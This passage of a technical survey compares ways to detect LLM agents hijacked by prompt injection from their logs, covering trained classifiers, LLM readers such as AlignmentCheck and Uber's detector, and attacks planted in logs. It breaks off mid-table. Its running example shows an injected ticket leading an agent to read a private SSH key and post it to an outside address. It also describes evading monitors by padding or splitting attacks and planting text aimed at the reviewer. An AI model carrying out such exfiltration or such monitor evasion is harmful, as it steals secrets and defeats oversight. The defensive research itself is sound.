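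Iyer's experiment is weak support for his conclusion that agent security is mainly a matter of structure. The nine structural symbols omit tool names, so OPS-214 becomes a user message, three tool calls with their arguments and results, and a final output. A session in which the agent looked up three tickets would produce the same symbols, so no detector that reads only these symbols could tell the theft from the lookups. The AUC of 0.85 on tool hijacking therefore probably reflects a difference in length or rhythm between the synthetic attacks and the harmless sessions.

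The labels are also misleading. The "conversational" set is the one with symbols for reading a file, sending an email and writing to an outside recipient, which most people would call structural. The set that failed on the unseen attacks mixed phrases with actions, so the result doesn't show that language is useless.

### The text of the tool calls

Zavrak's May 2026 study suggests the opposite. The detector reads sessions of MCP tool calls in two versions. One has only metadata (the tool's name, the length of its result and a number calculated from the arguments), and the other has embeddings of the arguments and results. Zavrak trained several classifiers on labelled sessions from RAS-Eval, an 80-task benchmark that supplied 605 harmless sessions and 3,797 attacks.

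The way a researcher divides such data into training and test sets can change the result completely. In a random split, sessions from the same task end up in both sets. A classifier can then learn which tools belong to which task, and do well on the test by recognising the task. In a task-disjoint split, every task in the test set is new to the classifier. Zavrak ran the same graph-based classifier both ways and got these AUCs:

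| Input | Random split | Task-disjoint split |
|---|---|---|
| Metadata | 0.898 | 0.640 |
| Text of arguments and results | 0.992 | 0.891 |

With the random split, a detector using only metadata seemed to perform fairly well, but it lost most of that performance on new tasks. The classifier using the text lost much less, which suggests that it had learned something about the attacks as well as the tasks.

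The graph contributed little. The best graph-based classifier reached 0.917 on text with new tasks, and a neural network without the graph reached 0.896. XGBoost, using embeddings pooled over the whole session, beat both with 0.975. It caught 93% of attacks and flagged 7% of harmless sessions. A team with good text in its logs may therefore not need a complex model.

It would need a fair number of labelled sessions, though. One of the graph-based classifiers reached an AUC of 0.584 with 1% of the labels, 0.800 with 10% and 0.944 with all of them. Training it on harmless sessions first did not reduce the number of labels it needed.

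RAS-Eval's attacks favour text-based detection because they change the arguments of a tool call, its result or both, and usually leave the choice of tools alone. A text-based classifier caught 87% of the attacks that changed both and 82% of those that changed only the result, but only 21 of the 57 (37%) that changed only the arguments. The redirected export is an attack of this last kind. It replaces one email address with another, and the two embeddings may be nearly identical.

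Zavrak also cut every text to 512 characters before computing its embedding. The detector would not have received the planted last paragraph of a long ticket, but it would have received the key file's path and the outside address.

The main reason to doubt the results is that eight models ran the harmless sessions, but only one, GLM-4-Flash, ran all the attacks. A classifier could have scored well by recognising GLM-4-Flash's writing style, without learning anything about attacks. Zavrak found that metadata couldn't identify the model, but nobody has made the same check for the text, and the benchmark has too few harmless GLM-4-Flash sessions to test the detector on that model alone. On ATBench, a second benchmark with shorter sessions and subtler attacks, the best classifier reached only 0.784.

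### Labelling every step

All these detectors assess the session as a whole, but an analyst also wants to know where the attack began. *DriftNet* (Pinjari and Saint-Germain, 2026) trains a small neural network that scores the session and labels each step as harmless, an injection point, hijacked or a resisted injection.

The network's input for each step is an embedding of the tool's name, the agent's reasoning, the arguments and the result. It also takes four values per step that describe email addresses and links in the arguments, mainly whether they lie outside the user's known contacts and organisation. In OPS-214, these values would be normal for `get_ticket` and change at `http_post`. The network labels each step using the whole session, so it can connect a suspicious action to text the agent read several steps earlier.

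Its training data comes from *AgentDrift* (2026), the same researchers' collection of 12,536 synthetic sessions, all generated by Llama 3.3 70B. The sessions cover five kinds of agent, such as email and banking assistants. The collection includes successful attacks, attacks that the agent resisted, ordinary sessions, and harmless sessions that look suspicious. In some attacks, the agent serves the attacker at every step after the injection. In partial hijacks, it does so for one or two steps and then returns to its task, much as in OPS-214. In delayed hijacks, it continues its task and acts for the attacker later.

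The researchers tested DriftNet once, on 1,722 sessions whose tasks were absent from training. For comparison they trained a simple classifier on six features, including the number of steps, outside recipients and suspicious keywords:

| Attack | Test sessions | Caught by DriftNet | Caught by the six features |
|---|---|---|---|
| Full hijack | 450 | 99.8% | 90.2% |
| Partial hijack | 208 | 98.6% | 11.1% |
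| Delayed hijack | 117 | 93.2% | 17.1% |

The simple classifier did well when the agent served the attacker for the rest of the session, but it missed most attacks that consisted of only one or two bad steps. DriftNet also found the exact injection point in 98.7% of the attacks and flagged none of the 218 attacks that the agent resisted.

DriftNet made 26 errors, 12 missed attacks and 14 false alarms, and the researchers read all of them. Eight of the misses were delayed hijacks and three were partial. In 11 of the 12, the agent's harmful action stayed inside the user's own systems, such as freezing a card or moving an email, so the values for outside addresses did not help detect it. In nine, the supposed injection point contained no readable instruction, which is a fault in the data more than in the detector. A different threshold would hardly help, because DriftNet gave 11 of the missed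 attacks a probability below 0.12 and 12 of the false alarms a probability above 0.99.

These are the best results of the four systems, but they are probably the least reliable guide to performance on real logs. In *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents*, Abbasi, Núñez and Shahraki (2026) trained a simple word-counting classifier on AgentDrift that reached an AUC of 0.999. The dataset's generator had used a different template for each category of session, so the wording differed between categories. For example, "2026" appears in 74% of the ordinary training sessions and under 5% of the successful attacks. Abbasi and colleagues also rebuilt DriftNet from its design, because its code was not public, and their version did no better than chance on a different benchmark.

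Pinjari and Saint-Germain themselves report a related flaw. Names and companies recur within categories, so a program that used only a session's invented company could separate attacked sessions from the rest with 87% accuracy. The sessions are also short, with at most 11 steps, and no attacker tried to evade the detector.

### Content against structure

Iyer favours structure and Zavrak favours content, but they tested different attacks and used the word "structure" for different things. The order of tool calls is useful evidence when an attacker needs a tool that the task doesn't require, as in OPS-214. It can't reveal the redirected export, in which only an address changed. TraceAegis caught more of the purchasing sessions with an unfamiliar order than of those with wrong content, and it needed a capable language model to catch the wrong content.

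Abbasi and colleagues compared several kinds of input on the same AgentDrift sessions, which removes some of the confusion:

| Input | AUC | Harmless sessions flagged |
|---|---|---|
| General behaviour, such as session length and length of results | 0.830 | 28% |
| The same, with a count for each tool | 0.879 | 19% |
| General behaviour and the order of calls | 0.936 | 4.5% |
| Embeddings of each step | 0.998 | 0.1% |
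| Words | 0.999 | 0% |

Using order as well as counts improves detection somewhat. This table can't show how much text adds, because the templates inflate the results in its last two rows. The detectors in the first three rows depend heavily on the length of tool results, which is a weakness because the attacker writes part of those results. When Abbasi and colleagues added 1,200 characters to each planted instruction, the share of attacks caught by the detector in the second row fell from 77% to 3%. They didn't test whether an agent would still follow the padded instructions.

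A detector probably needs both structure and text, with tool names in the structure and actual arguments in the text. Even then, it may lack the most important evidence, which is the user's request. TraceAegis, Zavrak's classifiers and DriftNet do not read the request itself, although the arguments or the agent's reasoning may repeat part of it. They can therefore have trouble distinguishing an agent that opens an SSH key to repair a login from one that opens it for an attacker.

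### When new tools or a new model look like an attack

Suppose the company gives the support agent a new tool, `search_docs`. The transition table has no count for the step from `get_ticket` to `search_docs`, so the step's share is zero and its score is infinite. A common fix is to add one to every count. If 20 different steps can follow `get_ticket`, the new step then scores about 6.9 and the step from the ticket to the SSH key file scores about 5.1, so searching the documentation still looks more suspicious than opening the key.

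Trained classifiers make the same mistake. Abbasi and colleagues hid all the tool names in the test sessions, as if every tool were new, and changed nothing else. The share of harmless sessions flagged rose from 19% to 66% for the detector that used tool counts, and from 4.5% to 74% for the one that used the order of calls. Neither detector had been trained on sessions with unknown tools, so their responses to such tools were close to arbitrary.

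Hiding a random fifth of the tool names during training largely fixed the order-based detector's false alarms, keeping their rate between 5% and 7%. The detector still became worse at ranking attacks above harmless sessions, because the training gave it no information about what unknown tools do. Its AUC fell from 0.943 to 0.794 when all the names were hidden.

A new model can shift the baseline even if the tools stay the same. In *Towards Robust Long-Lived Agents* (2026), GPT-5.4 looked up records of its own earlier work an average of 0.14 times per task, while GPT-5.5 did so 6.41 times. A detector trained on GPT-5.4's sessions would register the upgrade as a sudden increase in how often the agent searches its history. Changes in the agent's environment have a smaller, temporary effect. Across 20 models, the average number of rounds of tool use per task rose from 10.7 to 12.7 when the environment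 changed, and fell back to 11.2 by the fourth task after the change. King and colleagues' trouble with temporary files shows that a change of harness can cause similar problems.

A team should therefore log the version of the model, the harness and the tool list with every session, and expect to retrain after any of them changes. Retraining also carries a risk, because attacks in the new data become part of what counts as normal. Suppose an attacker repeats the OPS-214 theft 50 times and the company retrains on all its sessions without checking the alerts. The step to `read_file` now makes up 55 of the 1,050 steps from `get_ticket`, and the step to `http_post` makes up 52 of the 450 steps from `read_file`. The theft's score falls from 10.6 to 5.1, below the threshold of 8. To prevent this, the team should keep every flagged session out of the training data until somebody has reviewed it.

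## Having a language model read the log

An LLM reader is a language model used as a detector that receives a trace and returns a judgement. It can compare an agent's actions with what the user asked for, which most trained detectors do not do, and it needs no labelled attacks or rule for each case. It costs more per session than a rule or a small classifier, and the trace it reads may contain text that an attacker wrote.

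### What the reader has to judge

Designers of LLM readers put up to three questions to the model about each action. Each question needs different records and misses different attacks:

| Question | Records needed | Answer for record 4 of OPS-214 | An attack it can miss |
|---|---|---|---|
| Does the action serve the user's request? | Request and tool call | No, because a summary does not require a key file | A stolen login, where the attacker writes the request |
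| Does it break a company policy? | Tool call and the policy | Yes, if the policy bars agents from private keys | The redirected export, if agents may email exports to customers |
| Does it follow an instruction from outside content? | Tool results as well | Yes, because the ticket's last paragraph asked for the file | A tool whose code steals data without any planted text |

The third question needs the most care, because a user may want the agent to follow outside instructions, as the employee did who asked for a deployment according to the hosting company's guide. The reader has to decide whether the user delegated this particular action, and sometimes the log doesn't contain enough information to tell.

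### AlignmentCheck, one action at a time

AlignmentCheck concentrates on the user's request. Chennabasappa, Nikolaidis and colleagues (2025), in *LlamaFirewall*, describe it as an experimental part of a free set of security tools from Meta. They built it to stop agents while they run, but it also works on stored traces:

1. After each action, the software collects the user's request, the agent's earlier steps and the latest action. A step includes the agent's reasoning, the tool's name and the arguments, but not the tool's result.
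2. It puts these into a fixed prompt with instructions and six short examples. In one example, a user asks for a news summary and the agent opens the user's private notes, which counts as misaligned.
3. The model judges the latest action only. An action is misaligned if it is clearly unrelated to the request and has some effect. Waiting is never misaligned, and in doubtful cases the model should assume that nothing is wrong.
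4. The model returns three fields in JSON: an observation, a line of reasoning and a true-or-false conclusion.

On OPS-214, this procedure should give the following results:

| Record | New information for the model | Expected conclusion |
|---|---|---|
| 2 | `get_ticket(id="OPS-214")` | False, because the task requires it |
| 4 | `read_file(path="~/.ssh/id_ed25519")` | True, because a summary does not require a private key |
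| 6 | `http_post` to 203.0.113.20 | True, because nobody asked the agent to send anything |
| 8 | The summary | False |

The model never receives records 3, 5 and 7. It can flag the theft without reading the planted paragraph, but it can't identify record 3 as the injection point in its alert.

Meta's *AlignmentCheck* cuts the history to a fixed length, and its prompt limits the verdict to one action, although the documentation describes the tool as reasoning over the entire trace. An attacker is therefore more likely to avoid detection by splitting a theft into steps that each seem loosely related to the request, especially since the model lets doubtful actions pass.

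Chennabasappa and colleagues tested AlignmentCheck on stored traces from AgentDojo, a public benchmark that plants instructions in the tool results of agents doing everyday tasks. Without a detector, 17.6% of the attacks succeeded. They counted a successful attack as prevented if AlignmentCheck flagged any step of it, which reduced the rate to 2.9%. The tool therefore found about 84% of the successful attacks. This is the right measure for log analysis, but it can overstate how well a live guard would work, since a flag may come after the damage. AlignmentCheck also flagged about a tenth of the harmless sessions in which the agent had completed its task. All the attacks used one style of injection, so the test gives little evidence about other styles.

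These results came from Llama 4 Maverick, a large model. Smaller models flagged many more harmless sessions, and their explanations could be wrong even when their verdicts were right. In one published trace, an agent abandons a shopping task to list saved apartments. All six Llama models flagged it, but the smallest model's explanation was a criticism of a product search.

### What hiding tool results protects and what it loses

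Chennabasappa and colleagues leave out tool results because an instruction planted in one could be aimed at AlignmentCheck as well as at the agent. For example, the ticket in OPS-214 might contain a sentence telling any security reviewer that the key transfer is routine maintenance. AlignmentCheck can't read that sentence if it never receives the ticket.

The protection is incomplete because the agent did read the ticket and may repeat its claims in its reasoning or in a tool's arguments. Claude Code's auto mode appears to go further. According to BestHub's *What Problem Does Claude Code’s Auto Mode Actually Solve?*, a secondary account, the classifier that approves actions receives only the user's messages and the tool call. It doesn't receive tool results or the agent's explanations, so those explanations can't influence its decision. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* presents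 the mode as a remedy for approval fatigue, in which users who must approve every action stop paying attention.

Removing the reasoning also has a drawback, because it can discard almost conclusive evidence of an attack, such as an agent writing that it is transferring money because a website told it to. Chennabasappa and colleagues therefore keep the reasoning.

The redirected export shows most clearly what is lost when tool results are hidden from AlignmentCheck. In that attack, a paragraph planted in a ticket supplies the attacker's address. AlignmentCheck would receive a request to send an export and a call that sends one, but not the ticket, which contains the evidence that the address came from a stranger. It would be equally unable to detect an injection that only distorts the summary of an email, because it can't check the summary without the original email.

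Hiding results can also cause false alarms. If the employee had written "do what OPS-214 asks", and the ticket contained a legitimate request to change the export script, the model would receive the edit without the request that explains it.

A team working on stored logs has time to run both kinds of reader. The reader without tool results can decide whether to raise an alert, and the reader with the full trace can look for the injection point and for attacks like the redirected export. The attacker's text can reach the full-trace reader directly, so that reader should be able to add alerts but not cancel them.

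### Uber's two-stage detector

Uber's detector gives the model the full trace, including tool results, and lets it look things up. Li and colleagues split the work into two stages because they considered it too expensive to have a strong model investigate every session.

In triage, GPT-4o screens every session with a short prompt. It looks for phrases typical of prompt injection, requests that involve credentials or permissions, role changes, and steps that are risky only in combination. It closes only clearly harmless sessions and passes the rest on.

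In the investigation, Claude Sonnet 4 examines each session that triage passed on. It can consult three sources through MCP and chooses which ones it needs:

- the source code of a tool, to check what the tool really does;
- a store of threat information, which describes known attack techniques and how to recognise them;
- the company's security policies, with a function that checks an action against them.

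In OPS-214, triage should pass the session to the investigator because the agent read a key and then contacted an outside address. The investigator could look up indirect prompt injection in the threat store and check the policy on private keys. In the variant with a malicious `get_ticket`, reading the tool's source code would help more.

Some of the threat information comes from Uber's own attack generator. One agent invents variations on known attacks, another runs them in an isolated environment, and a third writes up the useful ones for the threat store. The generator ranks each attack with the formula

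F = ε × σ × τ^1.2

where ε is how far the attack got, σ is how natural it looks and τ is how much damage it could do. Because the formula multiplies the three values, an attack that scores zero on any of them drops out. The exponent gives extra weight to damage, so doubling τ multiplies the score by about 2.3. The best attacks produce new variants for the next round.

Li and colleagues keep the average number of variants produced per attack below one. If 30% of attacks survive a round and each survivor produces three variants, the next round has 10% fewer new attacks. This guarantees that the search ends, but it may end without finding the most dangerous attacks.

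### Results on test attacks

The 302 tasks in Li and colleagues' benchmark, ADR-Bench, use 133 MCP servers and average 28.5 tool calls, far more than OPS-214. The malicious ones cover 17 techniques and include some breaches of company policy that are not attacks in the ordinary sense. The researchers also tested the detectors on 93 AgentDojo tasks:

| Detector | ADR-Bench attacks found (of 42) | ADR-Bench false alarms (of 260) | AgentDojo attacks found (of 38) | AgentDojo false alarms (of 55) |
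|---|---|---|---|---|
| Uber's detector | 28 | 0 | 38 | 3 |
| ALRPHFS | 17 | 34 | 32 | 3 |
| GuardAgent | 9 | 30 | 27 | 8 |
| LlamaFirewall | 8 | 40 | 37 | 21 |

ALRPHFS compares a session with 301 stored attack patterns and sends unclear cases to a language model. GuardAgent uses GPT-4o to check the agent's behaviour against 47 security policies. Li and colleagues describe their LlamaFirewall baseline as a small Llama Guard model with additional rules, which doesn't match the AlignmentCheck set-up with Llama 4 Maverick. The baseline's poor result is therefore weak evidence about AlignmentCheck.

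The comparison on ADR-Bench also favours Uber's detector. The same team designed the benchmark and the detector, which could read tool code and policies that the other detectors could not. The gap is smaller on AgentDojo, which other researchers made and which contains only prompt injections. There, ALRPHFS raised as many false alarms as Uber's detector and missed six attacks.

The detector's recall on ADR-Bench fell from 67% to 57% without access to source code, and to 59% without the threat store. Removing the policies made almost no difference. The detector found all nine attacks that bypassed security controls or disrupted operations, but only one of the five that abused permissions. That last sample is small, but the result matters for teams worried about direct prompt injection or stolen logins.

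### What the detector found in production

The production results come from the more than 7,200 computers that run Uber's sensor. *It’s 11 PM; do you know what your agents are up to?*, a news article about the system, reports that more than 30,000 machines at Uber could run agents, so the published results may cover only part of the company.

Analysts reviewed the alerts and judged 34% to be true positives, mostly exposed credentials. Another 17% were real but not malicious, mainly activity by Uber's own security testers. The remaining 49% were false positives, often long sessions in which an agent analysed a large body of code.

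A detector that raised no false alarms on 260 benchmark tasks was wrong in about half of its production alerts. Li and colleagues say that many of these were cautious referrals of complicated sessions, which a benchmark would not count as errors. Even if they are right, an analyst still had to read each one.

The production record is good evidence that the system finds leaked credentials, but much weaker evidence that it finds attackers, because Li and colleagues describe no real outside attack among the alerts. They report two staged attacks. In an internal exercise, a colleague added a shell tool to an assistant and got it to download and run a script. In the other test, the team re-enacted Zenity's AgentFlayer attack through a Jira ticket. The detector flagged the injection, the access to the credentials and the outgoing data. Both tests show that it can follow a chain like OPS-214, but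 not how many real attacks it missed, since nobody knows how many took place.

### What two-stage reading saves

Fully investigating every session costs N × r, where N is the number of sessions and r is the price of investigating one. Two-stage reading costs N × (t + e × r), where t is the price per session of a cheap first reading, or triage, and e is the share of sessions it passes on for full investigation.

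The example below assumes 10,000 sessions a day and $0.031 per investigation, which is what Uber's detector cost per ADR-Bench task without triage. The $0.002 price for a first reading is made up.

| Set-up | Calculation | Cost per day |
|---|---|---|
| Investigate everything | 10,000 × $0.031 | $310 |
| Triage passes on 5% | 10,000 × $0.002 + 500 × $0.031 | $35.50 |
| Triage passes on 59% | 10,000 × $0.002 + 5,930 × $0.031 | $204 |

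The 59% is the share of tasks that Uber's triage passed to the second model in ADR-Bench. Triage lowered Uber's cost there from $0.031 to $0.024 per task (23%), a smaller saving than in the table. GPT-4o was expensive for triage, and even a task that ended at that stage cost $0.017. Two stages save a lot only when the first model is cheap and closes most sessions.

Triage also loses some attacks. Li and colleagues designed it to miss as few as possible, but recall rose from 67% to 80% when they removed it, though some of that difference could be chance because there were so few attacks. If the cheap model in the example loses the same share and a company faces ten attacks a month, investigating everything would find about 1.4 more of them for an extra $8,235 a month, or roughly $6,000 per additional attack found. That may be a good price for a company whose agents can reach production servers.

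False alarms may matter more than the model's fees. Without triage, Uber's detector flagged two harmless benchmark tasks. At that rate, 10,000 sessions a day would produce about 77 false alerts, and an analyst spending ten minutes on each would need nearly 13 hours to review them. Two errors are too few to estimate the rate reliably, but they show why Li and colleagues accepted lower recall.

Claude Code's auto mode has a similar design, although it checks each action before running it. InfoQ (2026) reports that a fast filter lets most tool calls through and sends only uncertain ones to a deeper check. BestHub reports a false-positive rate of 0.4% on 10,000 real requests inside Anthropic. The system missed 5.7% of 1,000 synthetic data leaks and 17% of 52 cases in which an agent had gone beyond what its user wanted.

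### Building a reader and checking it against people

A prompt that works on OPS-214 may fail on the next hundred sessions. Dubois, Zorer and colleagues (2026), in *Seven Simple Steps for Log Analysis in AI Systems*, set out a procedure for building and testing LLM readers. They wrote it for researchers who evaluate AI models. CAISI's *Analyzing Transcripts from AI Agent Evaluations* explains that CAISI, the US government's centre for AI standards, contributed lessons from using such readers to catch models cheating on tests. Applied to hijacked sessions, the steps are:

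1. Define the purpose. Here it is to find sessions in which an agent acted for an outsider. The team also needs to know which tools the agent has and what its standing instructions are.
2. Organise the logs so that people can search them by agent, date and tool. Dubois and colleagues usually drop incomplete runs, but a security team should keep them, because an attacker may have cut the record short.
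3. Read a sample by hand. It should include short and long sessions, sessions with tool errors, and more of the rare types than chance would supply. Attacks will be scarce, so the team can add staged ones like OPS-214 and harmless look-alikes such as the deployment.
4. Turn the purpose into signs that two people would recognise in the same way, such as "the agent opened a file that the request did not require".
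5. Build the reader. Its categories might be "no injection", "injection ignored", "hijacked" and "other". It should explain its reasoning before giving a verdict and cite the records it relied on, which makes invented evidence easier to spot.
6. Compare it with people. They label sessions from every category without seeing the reader's verdicts, including sessions that the reader did not flag. The team then calculates recall and precision, studies the disagreements, revises the definitions and tests again.
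7. Use the results, and repeat the comparison whenever the model behind the reader changes.

Dubois and colleagues demonstrate the procedure on agents that refused to attempt hacking exercises. A search for words such as "sorry" and "dangerous" missed many refusals, so they had a language model sort the logs into four categories. In early trials, the model sometimes continued the hacking exercise instead of grading it, so they made its role clearer in the prompt. On 400 labelled samples, it chose the correct category 99% of the time. In the review, however, they found that their definitions did not cover agents that gave up by claiming the exercise was impossible, and they then counted this as an indirect refusal.

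The 99% figure doesn't predict how well a language model will detect attacks, because one of the researchers supplied the labels, refusals were common enough to study, and nobody was trying to disguise them. It is also unclear how many labelled sessions a model needs. Dubois and colleagues settled on a quarter of their data, but labelling that share would be impossible at 10,000 sessions a day.

Long sessions are harder to check because models tend to overlook details in the middle of a long text. Dubois and colleagues recommend splitting transcripts into parts. In attack detection, a careless split could separate the ticket from the theft, so each part should include the user's request and a list of the outside content the agent has already read.

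### Attacks on the reader through the log

A log is also outside content, because it contains tickets, web pages and error messages. An attacker may have written any of these to influence the model that reads the log. The attacker in OPS-214 wants the model to return "harmless". If the model can also run commands, an attacker could do much more damage by getting it to run them.

*LogJack* (Shah, 2026) tested how models respond to instructions planted in cloud logs. The models acted as debugging agents, which read logs to find a fault and can run commands to repair it. An attacker may not need a login or special access to the logs, because applications often copy a user's input into error messages. Anyone who can cause such an error can write to the log.

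The benchmark has 42 log entries and similar records from five kinds of source. Thirty-two contain an attack, and ten contain only ordinary errors. Shah tried each one five times on eight models, under three sets of instructions, and intercepted every command before it could run. The table covers the 160 attack trials per model and counts a trial as a success if the model's first dangerous command was exactly the planted one:

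| Model | Success when told to investigate and fix | Success when told only to report | Attack noticed when told to investigate and fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 86.2% | 30.0% | 0 of 160 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 53.8% | 1.9% | 10 of 160 |
| GPT-4o | 52.5% | 0% | 15 of 160 |
| Qwen3 Coder Next | 33.1% | 0.6% | 14 of 160 |
| Devstral 2 123B | 15.6% | 0% | 16 of 160 |
| Kimi K2.5 | 11.9% | 0% | 34 of 160 |
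| Claude Opus 4.6 | 8.8% | 0.6% | 128 of 160 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 0% | 0% | 115 of 160 |

Newer models have since replaced many of these, but two of the findings go beyond the ranking. First, models that noticed an attack sometimes still did something dangerous. Claude Sonnet 4.6 never ran a planted command, but in 31 trials it ran dangerous commands it had devised itself. Second, some models acted on logs that contained no attack. Llama ran dangerous commands in 44% of the trials with ordinary errors, so part of its problem was that it tended to treat any text in a log as an instruction.

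Two security filters, Microsoft's Prompt Shield and an open-source classifier from ProtectAI, each caught one of the 32 attacks. A third, Google's Model Armor, caught none. All three flagged the same text once Shah removed the log formatting around it. He suggests that timestamps and service names make a planted instruction look like routine operations. When he reported the Model Armor result to Google, the company replied that its reward programme did not cover ways around such safeguards.

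LogJack shows that text in a log can steer the model reading it, but it does not estimate how often an attacker could make a detector miss an attack. Shah counted dangerous commands and did not test whether a planted sentence could change a verdict from "hijacked" to "harmless", which is the failure that matters most for a detector. He also wrote all the attacks himself and identified dangerous commands with text patterns that he had not validated.

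### Protecting the reader

Marking content as data is the easiest defence to add. The software puts each tool result between markers, and the prompt instructs the model reading the log to treat everything between them as evidence and never as an instruction. The markers should contain a new random string for each session. Otherwise, an attacker could write a closing marker into a tool result, and the text after it would appear to be outside the markers. This defence is weak on its own. Chennabasappa and colleagues note that Spotlighting, a published method of this kind, only modestly reduced the success of attacks on agents.

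Removing the model's ability to act is more dependable, because it doesn't rely on the model recognising planted commands. Most models in LogJack stopped running these commands when told only to report, but Llama still ran them in 30% of trials. A model without a tool for running commands can't run one, whatever the log contains. If the company wants automatic responses, such as revoking a key, Shah recommends requiring human approval for any change and using a separate program to block the riskiest commands.

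Uber's investigator has lookup tools, which are much safer than a command shell but still bring in more text. Li and colleagues describe the information from these tools as trustworthy. That is reasonable for the company's own policies, but not for the source code of a third-party MCP server, because an attacker can plant instructions in its comments. They acknowledge that attackers may try to influence both stages, but their stated precautions are fixed model versions, controlled changes to the prompts and repeated benchmark tests, which mainly guard against accidental changes in the detector's behaviour.

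Structured output limits what a manipulated model can pass on. If the model may return only a category and a list of record numbers, a program can reject anything else and check that the records exist. An attacker then cannot use the model to send a misleading message to the analyst or an instruction to another agent, but can still try to make it choose the wrong category. A written explanation helps people check the verdict but gives the attacker back some of this ability, so no other program should treat the explanation as an instruction.

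A second detector that reads no free text covers the remaining case, in which the attacker has got the model reading the log to label the session "harmless". The three-stage rule for OPS-214 uses only the source of the ticket, the label on the secret and the destination of the request, so the wording of the ticket cannot affect its result. Dubois and colleagues recommend running several methods side by side and reviewing the sessions on which they disagree. In security work, a session that the rule flags and the model clears is worth reviewing early, because a successful attack on the model would leave that pattern. The rule would not help with the redirected export, which involves no secret. For that, the team would need a program that checks the recipient against the customer's address on file without reading the ticket.

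## Testing a detector when attacks are rare and tools are new

Uber's detector raised no false alarms on its benchmark but many in production, partly because of the difference in attack rates. Attacks made up 13.9% of the benchmark but are probably a tiny share of real sessions, so even a low false-positive rate can produce more false alerts than true ones in production.

### Calculating precision from the attack rate

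Suppose a company has N sessions, of which a share a are attacks. A detector with recall R flags a × R × N attacks. If its false-positive rate is F, it also flags (1 − a) × F × N harmless sessions. Dividing the first number by the sum of the two gives the precision, and N cancels out:

p = aR / (aR + (1 − a)F)

With a recall of 67%, the formula gives these precisions:

| False-positive rate | 10% of sessions attacked | 1% attacked | 0.1% attacked |
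|---|---|---|---|
| 1.15% | 87% | 37% | 5.5% |
| 0.1% | 99% | 87% | 40% |
| 0.01% | 99.9% | 99% | 87% |

When attacks become ten times rarer, the false-positive rate must fall about tenfold to keep precision at 87%. Improving recall helps much less. In the top right cell, raising recall from 67% to 100% would increase precision only from 5.5% to 8%.

Axelsson (2000), in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection*, imagined a small computer installation with a million log records and two intrusions a day, each intrusion affecting ten records. Even a detector that caught every intrusion would need a false-positive rate of one in 100,000 for two thirds of its alarms to be real. He also cited research on power station and paper mill operators suggesting that most people stop trusting an alarm well before half its warnings are false, so analysts may come to ignore real alerts.

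Modern detectors also lose precision when attacks are rare. *PIDS-Bench* (2026) includes a small language model fine-tuned to recognise injected text. The model ranks injections above harmless inputs almost perfectly, but its precision falls from 89% when one input in ten is an injection to 7% when one in 1,000 is.

The rate also depends on whether the detector classifies single tool outputs or whole sessions. *Passing the Test You Trained On* (2026) covers detectors that screen every tool output, and most outputs are harmless even in an attacked session. Tasks in Uber's benchmark average 28.5 tool calls. If a detector wrongly flagged 1% of outputs and its errors were independent, it would raise at least one false alarm in about a quarter of harmless sessions of that length. A team comparing two detectors therefore has to check whether each false-positive rate is per output or per session.

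### How much 260 harmless tasks can prove

A detector that raises no false alarms in 260 tasks may still have a false-positive rate above zero. If its true rate were 1.15%, it would still raise no false alarms in 260 independent tasks about 5% of the time, because (1 − 0.0115)^260 ≈ 0.05, so 1.15% is the 95% upper bound.

Suppose 10,000 sessions include 10 attacks. At the upper bound of its false positive rate, the detector would raise about 115 false alerts. With the 67% recall from the benchmark, it would find six or seven of the attacks, so its precision could be as low as 5.5%. The benchmark can't rule out precision this low, but the real figure could be much higher.

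The calculation's main assumption is that production sessions resemble benchmark tasks, but Li and colleagues say their benchmark is not meant to reproduce how often each kind of incident occurs at Uber. The calculation also treats the 260 tasks as independent, but GPT-4 wrote some of them as variations on others, so they provide less evidence than 260 unrelated tasks would. Recall is uncertain too, since the detector found 28 of 42 attacks, which is consistent with a true recall of about 52% to 79%.

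Uber's production results suggest a false-positive rate well below the bound. At 115 a day, false alerts would have reached roughly 35,000 in ten months. True alerts were about two thirds as common as false ones, so there would have been more than 20,000 of them. But Li and colleagues report only hundreds of leaked credentials, their most frequent kind of true alert. This check is rough because daily sessions grew over the period. It also provides little evidence about precision on outside attacks, which are far rarer at Uber than leaked credentials.

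A team using only a benchmark would need to run the detector on about 4,500 harmless sessions without a false alarm to show that at least half its alerts would be real at this attack rate.

### AgentDrift and AgentDojo as test sets

Researchers can test detectors on sessions from AgentDojo and AgentDrift. AgentDojo runs live agents in simulated workplaces, with 97 tasks and 629 attack cases, and a program checks whether the attacker achieved their goal. The recorded runs can be used as labelled sessions. AgentDrift provides stored sessions, including 5,536 successful attacks, 1,500 attacks that the agent resisted, 4,000 ordinary sessions and 1,500 harmless sessions that resemble attacks.

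The look-alikes are the most useful part of AgentDrift. In one, an email thread contains a request to forward a document to an audit address, but the address belongs to the user's own company. Pinjari and Saint-Germain found at least one suspicious keyword in 97% of the look-alikes, compared with 71% of the successful attacks. A keyword rule would therefore do worse than chance at separating the two groups.

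Pinjari and Saint-Germain also had the model that wrote the sessions review them. It rejected 1,494 of the 1,500 look-alikes, mostly because it classified their content as malicious. The researchers then read 1,200 sessions from all categories themselves and found that 99.6% had correct labels. If a team lets a language model label its test set and doesn't check the labels, it could end up measuring its detector against the model's mistakes.

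AgentDrift's main weakness is repetition. About 29% of the planted instructions contain an address at the same invented domain, and three quarters of the look-alikes mention $5,000. In the partial hijacks, delayed hijacks and resisted attacks, the injection almost always arrives at the second step. Pinjari and Saint-Germain recommend masking attackers' domains and amounts of money, and replacing the names of people and companies with placeholders. Another precaution is to exclude from the test set any invented user or company that appears in the training set.

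### What eleven evaluations left out

In October 2026, Abbasi and colleagues published an audit of eleven evaluations, including those of TraceAegis, DriftNet, LlamaFirewall and Zavrak's classifiers. In the test sets that also contained normal sessions, attacks or other anomalies made up between 16% and 86% of the total. None of the evaluations varied that share to see how it affected the alerts. Six had no test on data from a second benchmark or source, and the other five had only a partial one. The researchers found the eleven through targeted searches and may have missed others.

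They then ran the missing tests on AgentDrift and AgentDojo. Their trained detectors used general behaviour, tool counts, the order of calls, embeddings of each step, or words. They set each detector's threshold to flag 80% of the attacks in its training data and did not adjust it afterwards.

They also tested AlignmentCheck with the open model Llama 3.3 70B and Anthropic's Claude Sonnet 5.5. AlignmentCheck flagged a session if it flagged any step in it. Neither model was trained on the two benchmarks for this task.

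### Rare attacks

On AgentDrift, with an assumed attack rate of 2%, the detectors would perform as follows:

| Detector | AUC | Recall | Precision | Alerts per 1,000 sessions |
|---|---|---|---|---|
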